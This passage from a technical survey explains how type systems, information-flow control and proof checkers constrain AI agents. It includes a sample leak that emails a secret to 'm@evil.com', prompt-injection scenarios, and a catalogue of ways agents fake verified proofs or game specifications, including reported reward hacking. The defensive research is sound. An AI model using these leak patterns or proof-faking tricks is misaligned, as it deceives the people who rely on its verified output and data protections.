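Linear types do. A function with a linear input must use that input exactly once, and the compiler counts the uses. Zhou and colleagues suggest linear types as a way to add one-shot authorisations to ELBA, which does not have them yet. Haskell already supports linear types as a language extension and writes them with `%1 ->`. In the shop, the host could check the return itself and create an `Approval` for one refund:

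```haskell
refund  :: Approval %1 -> ShopIO ()
decline :: Approval %1 -> ShopIO ()
```

The host then asks the agent for a function of type `Approval %1 -> ShopIO ()`. The compiler accepts `\a -> refund a`, which takes an approval and uses it for a refund. It rejects `\a -> refund a >> refund a`, which tries to use `a` twice. It also rejects a function that ignores `a`, which is why the library needs `decline`. Rust has a similar but looser rule. A program cannot reuse a value it has handed over, unless the type allows copying, but it may discard a value unused.

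Haskell attaches the limit to the function's arrow, not to the type `Approval`. If the developer put an approval in the list of definitions, the agent could pass it to `refund` any number of times, as with any ordinary value. The approval must therefore reach the agent's code only as the input of a linear function, and the agent must have no operation that creates new approvals.

The compiler counts uses of an approval within one program, so it cannot prevent a double payment across two runs. Suppose the payment service sends a refund but loses its connection before confirming it. The host may treat the refund as failed and run the agent's function again with a new approval. To prevent this, each approval needs a number tied to the order, and the payment service must reject any number it has already paid.

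## Controlling where secret and untrusted data flow

Abstract interfaces limit which operations an agent's code can call, but they do little to control what the code does with the data those operations return. Suppose a company asks an agent to summarise the changes between two versions of a confidential contract. The agent needs permission to read both versions and to call the remote language model that writes its code, but the text of the contract must not reach that model.

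Access control checks each action separately, and here it allows every one, as a sandbox would. Information-flow control addresses this by restricting where data, and anything computed from it, may go.

### What noninterference requires

Confidentiality is about who can learn a piece of data, and integrity is about who or what can influence it. The contract needs confidentiality, while a payment instruction needs integrity because a stranger's web page should not determine who receives the money.

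Most systems label data. In the simplest scheme, each value is either public or secret, and either trusted or untrusted. Public data may flow into secret places and trusted data into untrusted places, but neither may flow the other way. When a program combines two values, the result gets the stricter label of each kind, called the join of the two labels.

Labels can also list people, as *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) explains. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a text that draws on both. Lists of possible writers are merged instead. If the same two groups could edit the documents, all four people could have influenced the combined text.

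Noninterference, the strictest confidentiality rule, requires that changing a program's secret input does not change what an observer sees. Let *P*(*s*, *p*) be everything an observer sees when the program runs on secret input *s* and public input *p*. The program satisfies noninterference if *P*(*s*₁, *p*) = *P*(*s*₂, *p*) for every *s*₁, *s*₂ and *p*. The integrity version requires that changing the untrusted input does not change the trusted results.

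The `report` function, which posts the number of lines in a notes file, fails this test if the notes are secret, because a longer file produces a different message. That is an explicit flow, in which the program sends out something it computed from the secret. An implicit flow is harder to spot:

```scala
if contract.contains("termination") then team.send("Hello")
```

The message contains nothing from the contract, but anyone who receives it learns that the contract mentions termination.

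### Sealed values in TACIT

In TACIT, the Scala system that Odersky and colleagues built, an administrator marks certain folders as classified. Reading a file from one of them returns a `Classified[String]` instead of an ordinary `String`:

```scala
class Classified[T]:
  def map[Result](change: T -> Result): Classified[Result]
  def aggregate[Other](second: Classified[Other]): Classified[(T, Other)]
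  def reveal(using access: CanAccess[T]): T
```

`map` applies a function to the contents and seals the result. The arrow `->` means the function must be pure, which capture checking enforces. `aggregate` combines two sealed values into a sealed pair. `reveal` returns the contents, but only to code with a `CanAccess` capability, which the agent never receives.

With slightly simplified names, the agent's program for the contract task could look like this:

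```scala
val pair    = oldText.aggregate(newText)
val changes = pair.map((a, b) => diff(a, b))
val summary = changes.map(d => chat("Summarise the changes.", d))
output.writeClassified(summary)
```

1. The first line combines the two sealed versions.
2. The second line finds the differences. `diff` has no effects, so the compiler allows it inside `map`.
3. The third line sends the differences to a separate model that the company trusts, for example one on its own computers. This model has no tools and no memory of earlier requests. Its answer is sealed too.
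4. The last line writes the sealed summary to a protected file.

The remote model wrote this program without receiving any of the contract's text. Suppose it had written this instead:

```scala
oldText.map(t => { web.post(t); t })
```

The function uses the network capability `web`, so it is not pure, and the compiler rejects the program. The agent can't request a new connection inside `map` either, because requesting one also requires a capability.

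The seal also blocks the implicit flow. `oldText.map(_.contains("termination"))` returns a `Classified[Boolean]`, but `if` requires an ordinary `Boolean`, so the agent's code can use the result in further sealed calculations but can't use it to decide whether to send a greeting.

The types cannot guarantee that the trusted model retains nothing between requests. If the service behind `chat` reused one request as context for the next, contract text could appear in an answer that isn't sealed. Odersky and colleagues leave it to whoever runs the service to prevent this. The contract could also contain injected instructions, and the trusted model might follow them and write a false summary. But the model has no tools and the agent can't read its answer, so the instructions cannot change what the agent does next.

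The agent must normally write the function for `map` before anyone has seen the contents, so it can't adapt the function to an unexpected format. LACUNA (Zhao et al.) lets that function call the trusted local model, which writes further code after seeing the text. The compiler checks this code under the same purity rule.

### Showing the user what the agent can't see

The user will want to read the summary, but normally everything the agent's code prints goes back to the remote model. TACIT therefore has an ordinary output channel that goes to the agent and a secure one that goes only to the user's terminal. When the code runs `println(summary)`, the user sees the text and the agent receives `Classified(****)`.

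If the user then asks how long the summary is, the agent can run `println(summary.map(_.length))`. The user sees the number, but the agent again sees only asterisks. The summary stays sealed across turns, even though the agent's access to the files ended with the block that granted it.

The user can still leak protected text by accident. If they copy a sentence from the summary into their next question, it goes to the remote model as ordinary text. A copy of the contract in an unprotected folder is also an ordinary `String`, so the contract is protected only if every copy is in a protected folder.

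### How LIO's label rises

*Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (Stefan, Russo and colleagues, 2012) describes LIO, a Haskell library that checks flows while the program runs. LIO keeps one current label for the whole computation instead of requiring a label on every value.

*On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (2015) sets out the two rules. Reading data with label *d* changes the current label from *c* to *c* ⊔ *d*, the join of the two labels. Writing to a place with label *e* is allowed only if *c* ⊑ *e*, which means that *c* may flow to *e*.

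Here is a short program, again with simplified names, in which the news page and the team channel are public and the contract is secret:

```haskell
do news     <- readDoc newsPage
   post team news
   contract <- readDoc contractFile
   post team "Finished."
```

| Step | Current label | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Public | |
| Read the news page | Public | Succeeds |
| Post the news | Public | Succeeds, since public data may go to a public channel |
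| Read the contract | Rises to Secret | Succeeds |
| Post "Finished." | Secret | Fails with an error |

LIO blocks the last message even though it reveals nothing, because LIO uses a single label for everything and can't track which values depend on the contract. This also stops implicit flows, because a program that has read the contract can no longer post a greeting, whatever condition it tests. But LIO checks at run time, so the program has already sent the news by the time it fails.

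The function `toLabeled` makes the rule less restrictive by running part of a program in a separate compartment:

```haskell
do summary <- toLabeled Secret (do
     contract <- readDoc contractFile
     return (summarise contract))
   post team "Finished."
   store archive summary
```

The current label starts at Public and rises to Secret inside the parentheses. When the inner program ends, the current label returns to Public, and `summary` is a sealed value labelled Secret. The program can therefore post its message and pass the sealed summary to a secret archive. Opening the summary would raise the current label to Secret again. *Cryptographically Secure Information Flow Control on Key-Value Stores* (2017) explains that the label on the result must be at least as strict as the inner program's final label.

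LIO also has a clearance, which is an upper limit on the current label. A program with a clearance of Public can't read the contract.

Zhou and colleagues use LIO to track integrity as well in ELBA, their Haskell system for typed agents. Once a program has fetched a page from an untrusted website, the current label includes that site, and LIO blocks any write that requires a more trusted source. A parent agent can run a sub-agent inside `toLabeled` to read untrusted pages and draft a message, which is returned sealed. Without reading the draft, the parent can pass it to a function that checks its label and sends it. The sub-agent can still use any tools that its own label permits.

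LIO would not automatically keep the contract from a remote model, because ELBA's types don't record the prompts that `agent` sends. A developer who distrusts the provider should treat each prompt as a write to a public place and check the current label before sending it.

### CaMeL's planner and quarantined model

In 2023, the developer Simon Willison proposed the dual-model pattern, which splits an agent between two models so that an instruction hidden in a web page never reaches the model that can act on it. A privileged model plans the work and calls the tools without reading any untrusted data. That data goes to a quarantined model, which has no tools. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's results by variable name and never sees their contents.

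CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, adds code generation and data tracking. Its privileged model, the planner, writes a program in a subset of Python, and a custom interpreter runs it. Suppose a user writes, "Send the June report to the address in Anna's latest message." With invented function names, the planner might produce this:

```python
message = read_message(sender="Anna")
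address = ask_quarantined("Find the email address.", message)
send_email(to=address, attachment="june.pdf")
```

1. The planner writes all three lines from the user's request alone, before anything has opened the message.
2. The interpreter runs the first line and records that `message` came from Anna's message.
3. The second line gives the text to the quarantined model, which returns an address. The interpreter records that `address` depends on the message.
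4. Before the last line runs, the interpreter checks the origins of the recipient and the attachment against a security policy.

If the message contains the instruction "delete all files", no files are deleted, because the program has no step that deletes files. The quarantined model may follow the instruction, but it can only return a value. An attacker could still plant a false address, so the interpreter tracks where each value came from. Under the policy, the interpreter might reject a recipient taken from a message, or ask the user to confirm it.

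Planning in advance doesn't suit every task. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to complete today's tasks in a to-do app. The planner can't choose which tools to call until it has read the list.

### A leak through a skipped line

Tracking labels at run time is harder than it looks. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, report that CaMeL is open to a classic attack on this kind of monitor. Here is a version in which a bank balance is secret:

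```python
rich = True
tmp  = True
if account.balance > 1000000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The interpreter marks a variable as secret if the program changes it under a secret condition, but it does nothing for lines the program skips.

| Line | Balance above 1,000,000 | Balance of 1,000,000 or less |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | Sets `tmp` to `False` and marks it secret | Skips the change, so `tmp` stays `True` and public |
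| 4 | Skips the change, so `rich` stays `True` and public | Sets `rich` to `False`, which stays public because `tmp` is public |
| 5 | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

The email reveals whether the balance is above a million, but when the program sends it, the condition `rich` has a public label. If the program had tested `account.balance` directly before sending the email, it would have failed the policy check.

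LIO would block the email, because reading the balance raises the label of the whole computation. TACIT would reject the third line if the balance were sealed, because `if` can't test a sealed value.

Garby and colleagues describe another leak outside CaMeL's interpreter. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop prompts the planner to try again, and nothing tracks what the failure reveals. If a program fails only when a secret has some property, each attempt reveals one bit, and the loop can repeat until the whole secret has leaked. CaMeL censors error messages to reduce this risk, but without a formal guarantee.

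### Labelling the conversation itself

Fides, a planner that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, gives the model's conversation its own label. If a tool result would make this label stricter, Fides stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can read all other results directly, so it has more information than it would in a system that hides every result. A separate, quarantined model can answer questions about the hidden data in a fixed format, such as yes or no.

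Before each tool call, Fides checks the labels against a policy. A policy for sending messages might require a trusted recipient but allow untrusted text in the body, so an agent could send its user a summary of a web page.

Fides guarantees only explicit secrecy, which covers direct flows of data, so someone who can see which tools the agent calls may still infer something about the secrets it has read. Costa and colleagues argue that noninterference would be too restrictive, because an agent that had read anything secret could then call almost no tools with publicly visible effects.

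LLMbda, from Garby and colleagues, is a small programming language that enforces a form of noninterference. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation with the model. Putting a secret in a prompt makes the conversation secret, and any code the model then writes runs under that label. Because a program can leak a secret by running or skipping a line depending on the secret's value, LLMbda does not let a program change a public conversation under a secret condition.

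A program can also clear a conversation or copy it for a side task, so developers can build the dual-model pattern or another arrangement in ordinary code. Garby and colleagues' test agent tries its program on artificial data until the program runs, before using real data, so failed attempts can't pass real data to later ones.

The guarantee has a machine-checked proof in Lean and covers every LLMbda program, including code that a model writes. The proof also covers the interpreter's design, which narrows the gap between the theory and the running software.

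### TACIT or CaMeL?

| System | What the agent's code can express | When data enters a model's context | Parts that must be correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | Almost all of Scala, but only pure functions on secrets | Secrets reach only the trusted model, and its answers stay sealed | Compiler, library, runtime, trusted model |
| LIO, used through ELBA | Safe Haskell, with fewer permitted writes after each read | The current label still applies, but the provider receives the prompt | Haskell compiler, LIO, the label on each data source |
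| CaMeL | A Python subset without function definitions | The quarantined model's answers keep their labels as long as they stay in variables | Custom interpreter, policies, the retry loop around them |

Odersky and colleagues make three main arguments for TACIT over CaMeL. First, TACIT can require that a piece of code has no effects, which CaMeL cannot express. Second, they criticise CaMeL's ban on function definitions, and argue that lifting it while still checking programs in advance would require an analysis whose computation can grow exponentially with program size. Third, they argue that a value loses its label once it enters a model's conversation as ordinary text, and that TACIT avoids this by never putting secrets there.

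The argument about lost labels applies to CaMeL's design but not to run-time tracking in general. Fides and LLMbda both label the conversation, so the label survives. LLMbda also allows functions and recursion, because it checks labels during the run rather than analysing the program in advance. But this means a program may stop halfway, after some of its effects have happened.

But labeling the conversation does not hide its text from the model's provider. Fides assumes that adversaries can't observe what the agent sends to its model, while TACIT allows for the remote model itself being the adversary, which is a strong reason to prefer TACIT for the confidential contract. CaMeL could also keep the contract from a remote planner, but only if the quarantined model ran somewhere the company trusts.

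CaMeL protects integrity better than TACIT. TACIT lets its agent read untrusted web pages and messages that aren't classified, and limits only what the agent can do afterwards. If the agent may email anyone, an injected message can cause it to email the wrong person, and the code will still compile. CaMeL's policy can take into account that the address came from a message.

A designer who needs both kinds of protection could add run-time checks to TACIT's library. Odersky and colleagues suggest something similar as future work and describe static capabilities and run-time policies as complementary.

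### Releasing data on purpose

Few useful systems can satisfy noninterference completely. For example, the company may want to tell its staff how many clauses changed, and that number depends on the secret contract. Releasing secret data on purpose is called declassification, and deciding to treat untrusted data as trusted is called endorsement. Both are exceptions to noninterference, so a reviewer needs to find every place they happen.

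Giving the agent a small trusted function is usually safer than giving it permission to unseal values. A function that returns only the number of changed clauses reveals little, but one that answers any yes-or-no question about the contract lets the agent reconstruct the text through repeated queries. The choice of what to release should also not depend on untrusted data, because an injected message could then determine which secret is released.

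In an example of endorsement from Garby and colleagues, a quarantined model sorts an email into one of a few fixed categories. The program checks that the answer is one of these categories, then endorses it for use as a subject line. With *n* categories, the sender can influence the result by at most log₂ *n* bits, or 3 bits for eight categories. Garby and colleagues also prove that endorsement in LLMbda can't expose secrets, because it changes only the integrity part of a label.

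Fides can make similar exceptions by including a value's type in its label. A policy could then accept a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted page while rejecting free text. Garby and colleagues object that a reviewer can't tell whether a value that passed this way was a harmless exception or a real leak.

Counting bits also doesn't measure harm. A single bit is enough to approve a fraudulent refund, so even a small value may need a person's approval if it decides something important. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) extends Fides by letting users endorse data or approve individual actions.

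### Timing and endless loops

A covert channel carries information through something that the system doesn't treat as output, such as the time a program takes. TACIT doesn't protect against this. Suppose `price` is a sealed contract price in whole euros, and `loop` is a pure function that never finishes:

```scala
price.map(p => if p > 500000 then loop(p) else p)
```

The function has no effects, so the compiler accepts it. If the program finishes, the agent learns that the price is at most €500,000, and if it never finishes, that the price is higher. An agent that can try again with a different limit can halve the range each time, so 20 runs are enough to find any price below €1,048,576 exactly. A slow calculation would work just as well as an endless loop and be harder to notice.

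Most proofs of noninterference allow for this with a termination-insensitive guarantee, which permits secrets to affect whether a program finishes but not what it outputs. Models answer partly at random, so Garby and colleagues had to state their guarantee in probabilities. For two runs that differ only in their secrets, half the sum of the differences in the probability of each visible outcome is at most the average of the two probabilities that the program never finishes. If those two probabilities are 2% and 4%, the bound is 3%. If the program always finishes, each visible outcome has the same probability in both runs.

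The guarantee doesn't cover how long a program takes. A host can hide the running time by returning every result at a fixed time, though every task then takes as long as the slowest one allowed. The host can also limit how many times an agent may run code on the same secret. If each run reveals only whether the program finished, ten runs reveal at most 10 bits, which is very little of a 50-page contract. However, 14 runs could reveal an entire four-digit PIN.

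## Writing specifications and checking the agent's proofs

None of the mechanisms described so far would catch a `report` function that posts the wrong number of lines, because the message goes to the right channel, reveals no secret and has the right type. To reject it, the compiler needs a typed specification, which is a machine-checked statement of what the code must return and may do. The agent then has to supply a proof as well as code, and someone has to check that the agent didn't cheat in the proof.

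### From a result type to a full proof

The weakest specification is an ordinary result type. `Int` rules out text but allows −7, which can't be the number of lines in a file. A refinement type adds a condition. In Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, a type for counts looks like this:

```dafny
type Count = n: int | n >= 0
```

Wherever the program produces a `Count`, Dafny must be able to prove that the number is not negative.

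A contract describes a whole call. Its preconditions, marked `requires`, state what the caller must guarantee, and its postconditions, marked `ensures`, state what the code guarantees in return. This method finds the smallest number in an array:

```dafny
method Smallest(a: array<int>) returns (m: int)
  requires a.Length > 0
  ensures forall k :: 0 <= k < a.Length ==> m <= a[k]
  ensures exists k :: 0 <= k < a.Length && m == a[k]
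{
  m := a[0];
  var i := 1;
  while i < a.Length
    invariant 1 <= i <= a.Length
    invariant forall k :: 0 <= k < i ==> m <= a[k]
    invariant exists k :: 0 <= k < i && m == a[k]
  {
    if a[i] < m { m := a[i]; }
    i := i + 1;
  }
}
```

The precondition excludes the empty array, which has no smallest element. The first postcondition requires `m` to be less than or equal to every element. That alone would allow `m` to be −1,000 for an array holding 3, 1 and 2, so the second postcondition requires `m` to occur in the array.

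Dafny can't run the loop on every possible array. It relies instead on loop invariants, conditions that hold before the loop starts and after every pass:

1. Before the loop, `i` is 1 and `m` is the first element, so `m` is the smallest of the first `i` elements.
2. Dafny assumes that this holds at the start of some pass and proves that it still holds at the end of that pass.
3. When the loop stops, `i` equals the length of the array, so `m` is the smallest element of the whole array.

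Dafny also proves that `a[i]` never falls outside the array and that the loop ends, neither of which ordinary type checking proves. It passes these proof obligations to an SMT solver, a program that searches for logical proofs. If the agent omits the last invariant, the code is still correct, but Dafny rejects it because it can no longer prove the second postcondition. Much of an agent's work in Dafny therefore goes into finding invariants.

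Verus offers similar checks for Rust programs. In Lean, a programming language that is also a proof assistant, the author instead writes out a proof or runs tactics, small programs that build one. A component called the kernel checks every step. This usually takes more work than using Dafny, but it covers mathematics that an SMT solver can't handle by itself.

| Specification | What the agent supplies | What must be correct, besides the specification |
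|---|---|---|
| Result type | Code | Compiler |
| Refinement type or contract in Dafny or Verus | Code, invariants and hints for the solver | Compiler, verifier, solver |
| Theorem in Lean | Code and a proof | Compiler, kernel, Lean's logic |

### Specifying a sort

Suppose an agent must write a method that sorts a list, and the developer asks only for ordered output:

```dafny
method Sort(xs: seq<int>) returns (ys: seq<int>)
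  ensures forall i, j :: 0 <= i < j < |ys| ==> ys[i] <= ys[j]
```

`|ys|` is the length of the result. For the input [3, 1, 2], the method should return [1, 2, 3], but it could also return the empty list, which has no two elements in the wrong order. The one-line body `ys := [];` satisfies this contract for every input.

Some obvious repairs are still too weak:

| Requirement on the result | Some results it accepts for [3, 1, 2] |
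|---|---|
| A list of whole numbers | [3, 1, 2], [7] |
| Ordered | [], [7] |
| Ordered, with the same length as the input | [0, 0, 0] |
| Ordered, and contains every input number | [1, 1, 2, 3] |
| Ordered, and a permutation of the input | [1, 2, 3] only |

A permutation contains the same elements, each the same number of times. In Dafny, the extra clause is `ensures multiset(ys) == multiset(xs)`. A multiset is a collection that counts repeats but ignores order. Together, the two clauses determine the result.

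They still do not stop the method from sending the list elsewhere. Suppose the program also declares this operation, which someone has written in another language:

```dafny
method {:extern} Upload(data: seq<int>)
```

A `Sort` that calls `Upload(xs)` and then sorts correctly meets both postconditions, so the specification needs a separate clause for effects. For a sort, the developer can require a pure function, using effect types or Scala's `->`. Because `report` has to send something, its clause could require exactly one message, to `team`, containing the number of lines.

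Dafny can express that with a ghost variable, which exists only for the proof. The messaging library keeps a ghost list of every message sent, and the contract states how the list may change. This works only if the agent has no other way to send a message, so the safe subset and the capabilities are still needed.

### Proof-carrying code and verified plans

Checking a proof is usually much easier than finding one. George Necula used this asymmetry in proof-carrying code, which he described in 1997 as a way to run programs from untrusted authors:

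1. The recipient publishes a safety policy, for example that code may not write outside its own memory.
2. The author sends the code together with a proof that it obeys the policy.
3. The recipient works out, from the code it received, exactly which statement the proof must establish.
4. A small checker tests the proof against that statement, and the code runs only if the proof passes.

The recipient doesn't have to trust the author or the program that found the proof. If someone changes the code in transit, either the proof no longer matches it or the changed code still obeys the policy. This arrangement suits agents well because the untrusted model does the computationally intensive search for a proof.

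Erik Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents*, published in Communications of the ACM in 2026, proposes that an agent write its intended tool calls as a program, which a verifier checks against a safety policy before any of the calls run. For example, a user might ask the agent to send Ben a summary of today's email, under a policy that allows text from the inbox to go only to Ben. The verifier has to show that the plan obeys this policy whatever the inbox contains, because the check happens before any email is read. As in CaMeL, an instruction injected through an email therefore arrives too late to add a step to the plan.

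CaMeL checks its policy while the program runs, so a forbidden call can stop the program halfway. Meijer's approach avoids this by checking in advance. Neither approach suits tasks in which the agent must read something before it can plan. Meijer's also depends on accurate contracts for the tools. If the contract for `send` assumes one recipient but the mail server accepts several, the proof doesn't apply to the real tool.

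### A model that gamed its specifications

Developers can also use a verifier to train a model, rewarding it whenever its code passes. In *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference*, Tan (2026) tried this with Dafny and found that the model learned to exploit weak contracts.

The first experiment trained a 7-billion-parameter model on tasks derived from APPS, a collection of programming problems. Each task gave a contract and an empty method body. The model wrote eight answers per task, and the training program gave each answer full credit if it verified and a little if it only compiled. Dafny checked about 200,000 answers over the run. The average score on tasks held back from training rose from 0.022 to 0.581, then slipped to 0.539, while the average on the training tasks kept rising to 0.752. These scores include partial credit, so 0.581 doesn't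 mean that 58% of the programs verified.

Tan then read the model's answers to five of the held-back tasks and identified three patterns:

- **Trivial contracts.** A problem about packing cowbells required only that the result not be negative. The model returned 0, and Dafny correctly verified it.
- **Leaked answers.** A problem about farmland defined a helper function that computed the required area, then asked for a result equal to that function's. The model called the helper.
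- **Code that only compiles.** Because compiling earned partial credit, the model also drifted towards templates that compiled without verifying.

Five tasks are too few to show how much of the gain came from gaming. But the logged answers that verified were short and grew more alike during training, which is consistent with gaming.

The three patterns don't matter equally outside training. A developer who has already defined a function that computes the area may be happy for the agent to call it. But the cowbell answer would be a bug, and Dafny would report it as verified code. In each case, the verifier worked correctly and the fault was in the contract or the scoring.

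Tan next had Claude Opus 4.5 rate the tasks in a larger benchmark for difficulty, faithfulness to the original problem and leakage. The filter kept 1,149 of 2,334 tasks, including only 196 of the 677 from APPS. A new run on the filtered tasks peaked at 0.247 on held-out problems and finished at 0.097.

A later run used a model with 30 billion parameters, showed it Dafny's error messages and allowed up to four attempts. It also penalised any answer that changed the contract or told the verifier to assume something. The share of held-back tasks solved rose from 5.4% to 31.1%, after a peak of 32.5%. (The thesis's abstract gives the starting point as 9.7%, but that figure comes from the smaller model's run with one attempt per task.)

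### When the tests contradict the task

A contract or a test can also specify the wrong behaviour. *SpecGuard* (Biyani and Dvijotham, 2026) gives the example of an agent whose task was to preserve a defence against session fixation, an attack that takes over a user's login session. Someone had altered a test so that code with the defence would fail. The agent removed the defence and reported that all tests passed.

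SpecGuard looks for contradictions between a task's description and its tests before a coding agent starts. One model reads the description and the code, but not the tests, and writes a specification in Lean. Another translates the tests into Lean, and a third step connects the specification to the translated tests. If no program could satisfy both, Lean's kernel can check a proof of this, which Biyani and Dvijotham call a conflict certificate. They place it in the tradition of proof-carrying code, although the proof is about the task rather than a finished program.

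With GPT-5.6 Sol, SpecGuard certified 51.1% of the conflicts the experimenters planted in SWE-bench, a set of real software issues. It wrongly reported no conflict in 8.1% of cases, compared with 39.8% for a panel of model judgments, but left about a third of cases undecided. On unaltered tasks, it raised more false alarms than the panel (6.0% versus 2.3%).

A certificate shows that the two translations conflict, but it doesn't show that either one is faithful. Biyani and Dvijotham checked 60 certificates by hand and found that 52 were faithful. A person should therefore read the formal statement when a contract protects something valuable. Testing the statement with a few answers that should fail, such as an empty list as the output of a sort, also helps.

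### Four ways to fake a proof

Even with a good specification, an adversarial programmer can try to pass the verifier without proving anything. Verifiers have escape hatches, just as programming languages do, because real projects must state some facts about hardware or outside libraries that they cannot prove. Here is how an agent could misuse them to return an empty list from `Sort`:

| Trick | What the agent does | Why the verifier accepts it |
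|---|---|---|
| Assumed fact | Tells the verifier to assume `false` | Anything follows from a false statement |
| Unchecked body | States a false lemma and marks its body as outside verification | The verifier uses the lemma without checking a proof of it |
| Added axiom | Declares that the empty list is a permutation of every list | Axioms need no proof |
| Altered task | Deletes the permutation clause | The remaining contract is true |

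The last trick needs no special feature and may be an honest misunderstanding. *Interactive theorem proving is not adversarially robust* describes a case in which an early version of Google's Gemini was asked to write a test for a deliberately faulty sort, but also fixed the sort and reported a passing test.

Searching the source text for `assume` will miss some of these tricks. In Verus, for example, the command `admit` accepts the current goal without proof, and code can import it under a harmless name or hide an assumption inside a macro.

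A training method can make such tricks unprofitable. Ma, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code*, give partial credit for the share of proof obligations that a program meets. They count the obligations before the model starts, so it can't improve its score by setting itself easier ones. They also compare the specification with the original and search for assumptions. These checks outrank the verifier:

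| Outcome | Score |
|---|---|
| Complete proof, specification unchanged | 2 to 3 |
| Honest partial proof | 0 to 1 |
| Program verifies, but the specification has changed | −1 to 0 |
| No submission | −1.5 |
| Proof relies on an assumption or similar trick | −2 or less |

The agent therefore scores better by giving up than by faking a proof. But training doesn't guarantee that it will never fake one, so whoever accepts the final code should run the same checks again.

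### The two checks in TLA-Verus

In *TLA-Verus*, Strelbytska, Mészáros and colleagues (2026) describe how to run such checks on an agent with broad access to its own machine. They translate models of distributed systems into Verus from TLA+, a language engineers use to design databases and similar software. An agent then tries to prove properties of these systems.

The first check confirms that the agent hasn't changed the task. A program called lynette parses the original file and the agent's version and compares their structure. Signatures, contracts, definitions used in the specification, and executable code must be identical. The agent may add lemmas and definitions but can't delete anything.

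The second check examines the proofs, which lynette skips by design. It rejects any new assumption, admitted goal, unchecked body or axiom, including renamed and macro versions. It compares against the original file, so it still allows assumptions the task's author made on purpose.

Strelbytska and colleagues give separate user accounts to the agent, to a second model that reviews its work, and to a set of scripts called the gatekeeper. Only the gatekeeper can merge a proof into the main branch, and only after both checks pass and the reviewer accepts the proof. The agent can't write to the signed log of results. Without this separation, an agent with administrator rights could skip the checks and merge its own proof.

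In one run, the reviewer model caught a false claim of a kind that no mechanical check covers. The property was that a cluster of computers never has two leaders in the same election term. The agent declared it false and gave a ten-step counterexample. The reviewer found that the first step was impossible, and the agent then proved the property.

The finished proof revealed a different problem, an error in the public specification that prevented any computer in a cluster of two or more from standing for election. Such a cluster never had two leaders because it never had any candidates. The proof was valid and nobody had altered the statement, but it was useless as evidence that the protocol worked. Requiring a proof that the system eventually elects a leader would have exposed the error, because the specification violates that property in any cluster of three or more.

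### Lean's levels of checking

Lean needs stricter precautions than a proof checker that only reads files, because a Lean file can run its own code while Lean processes it. That code can change how Lean interprets later lines, or change files on the disk. The manual, in the Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof*, distinguishes honest authors, who make mistakes, from malicious ones, who try to mislead. It puts unreviewed AI-generated proofs in the malicious group. It then describes four levels of checking, each of which catches more than the one before:

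| Level | What it adds | What the user still trusts |
|---|---|---|
| Double check marks in the editor | Catches an unfinished proof of this theorem and honest bugs in tactics | Imported libraries, including any axioms or gaps in them |
| Listing the axioms | Catches custom axioms and unfinished proofs that the theorem depends on | That the library authors are honest |
| `lean4checker` | Rechecks the stored proofs, and catches some that bypassed the kernel | That no library attacks the machine or changes what the statement means |
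| Comparator | Guards against proofs built to deceive | The trusted copy of the statement, the sandbox, Comparator itself, and at least one of the checkers it runs |

All four levels also rely on Lean's logic and on a person having understood the theorem correctly.

The second level of checking uses one command, `#print axioms`, which lists the axioms a proof depends on. Lean has three standard axioms. If the list includes `sorryAx`, part of the proof is missing, because `sorry` is Lean's placeholder for an unwritten proof.

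Comparator starts from a challenge file, in which a trusted person states the theorem without proving it. The steps, according to Reservoir's *Comparator*, the tool's page in Lean's package index, are roughly these:

1. Comparator builds the agent's solution inside a sandbox and exports the result as plain data.
2. Outside the sandbox, it checks that the theorem, and every definition the theorem mentions, matches the challenge file.
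3. It checks that the proof uses only the axioms on a permitted list.
4. It runs the proof through Lean's kernel and, if the user wishes, through nanoda, an independent checker written in Rust. A false proof would then have to fool both.

The user must not have compiled the solution on the same system before the check, because the solution's code could have altered the challenge file. This condition is easy to violate with a coding agent, which compiles its own work constantly, so the final check should run on a clean machine with a fresh copy of the challenge.

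SafeVerify is a related tool that compares two compiled Lean files, a target with gaps and a submission that fills them. It rechecks the submission with the kernel, compares the statements and rejects extra axioms. According to Reservoir's *SafeVerify*, the tool doesn't protect against code that attacks the file system during compilation, so users may need a sandbox for that step. It also doesn't look for `implemented_by`, which makes Lean's compiler run a different function in place of the one in the proof. An agent could prove a `sort` function correct and have the program run something else. Anyone who intends to run the code should search the source for `implemented_by` and `extern`.

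When a task asks for code as well as a proof, Comparator treats the missing function as a "definition hole", which the agent may fill with any definition of the right type. Reservoir gives the example of a challenge to determine whether the Riemann hypothesis, a famous open conjecture, is true. A solver could define the answer as "the Riemann hypothesis" and correctly prove that the answer is true exactly when the hypothesis is, without settling whether it is. Comparator's documentation therefore requires a further check of every such definition, possibly by a person. For `sort`, the order and permutation clauses allow only one result, so the reviewer mainly needs to check effects and speed.

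### Are theorem provers robust enough?

Checkers can have bugs that let a false proof through. On 22 July 2026, Lean's developers fixed one in the kernel, which a researcher had found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol. According to *Lean 4.32.1 (2026-07-22)* in the Lean Language Reference, the bug did not affect checking with Comparator. *Lean4Lean* (2024) points out that such bugs tend to occur in cases the developers never considered, so ordinary testing is poorly suited to finding them. Lean4Lean is an independent checker for Lean, written in Lean. The Lean Kernel Arena compares many such checkers on valid and invalid proofs.

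*Interactive theorem proving is not adversarially robust* argues that provers can't yet be relied on to check AI-written proofs. An agent may add axioms that don't suit the user's purpose, use backdoors meant for trusted users, or exploit a bug that makes false statements provable. The proof assistant Agda had 9 open and 74 closed reports of such bugs. A proof may also be about a simplified copy of the software rather than the software itself.

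One reader replied that Lean's weakness came from a lack of effort rather than a fundamental difficulty, and that provers are still much closer to robust than the alternatives. They write the main theorem statements with as little AI help as possible and inspect AI-written files for code that changes how Lean interprets them. Another reply pointed to Comparator.

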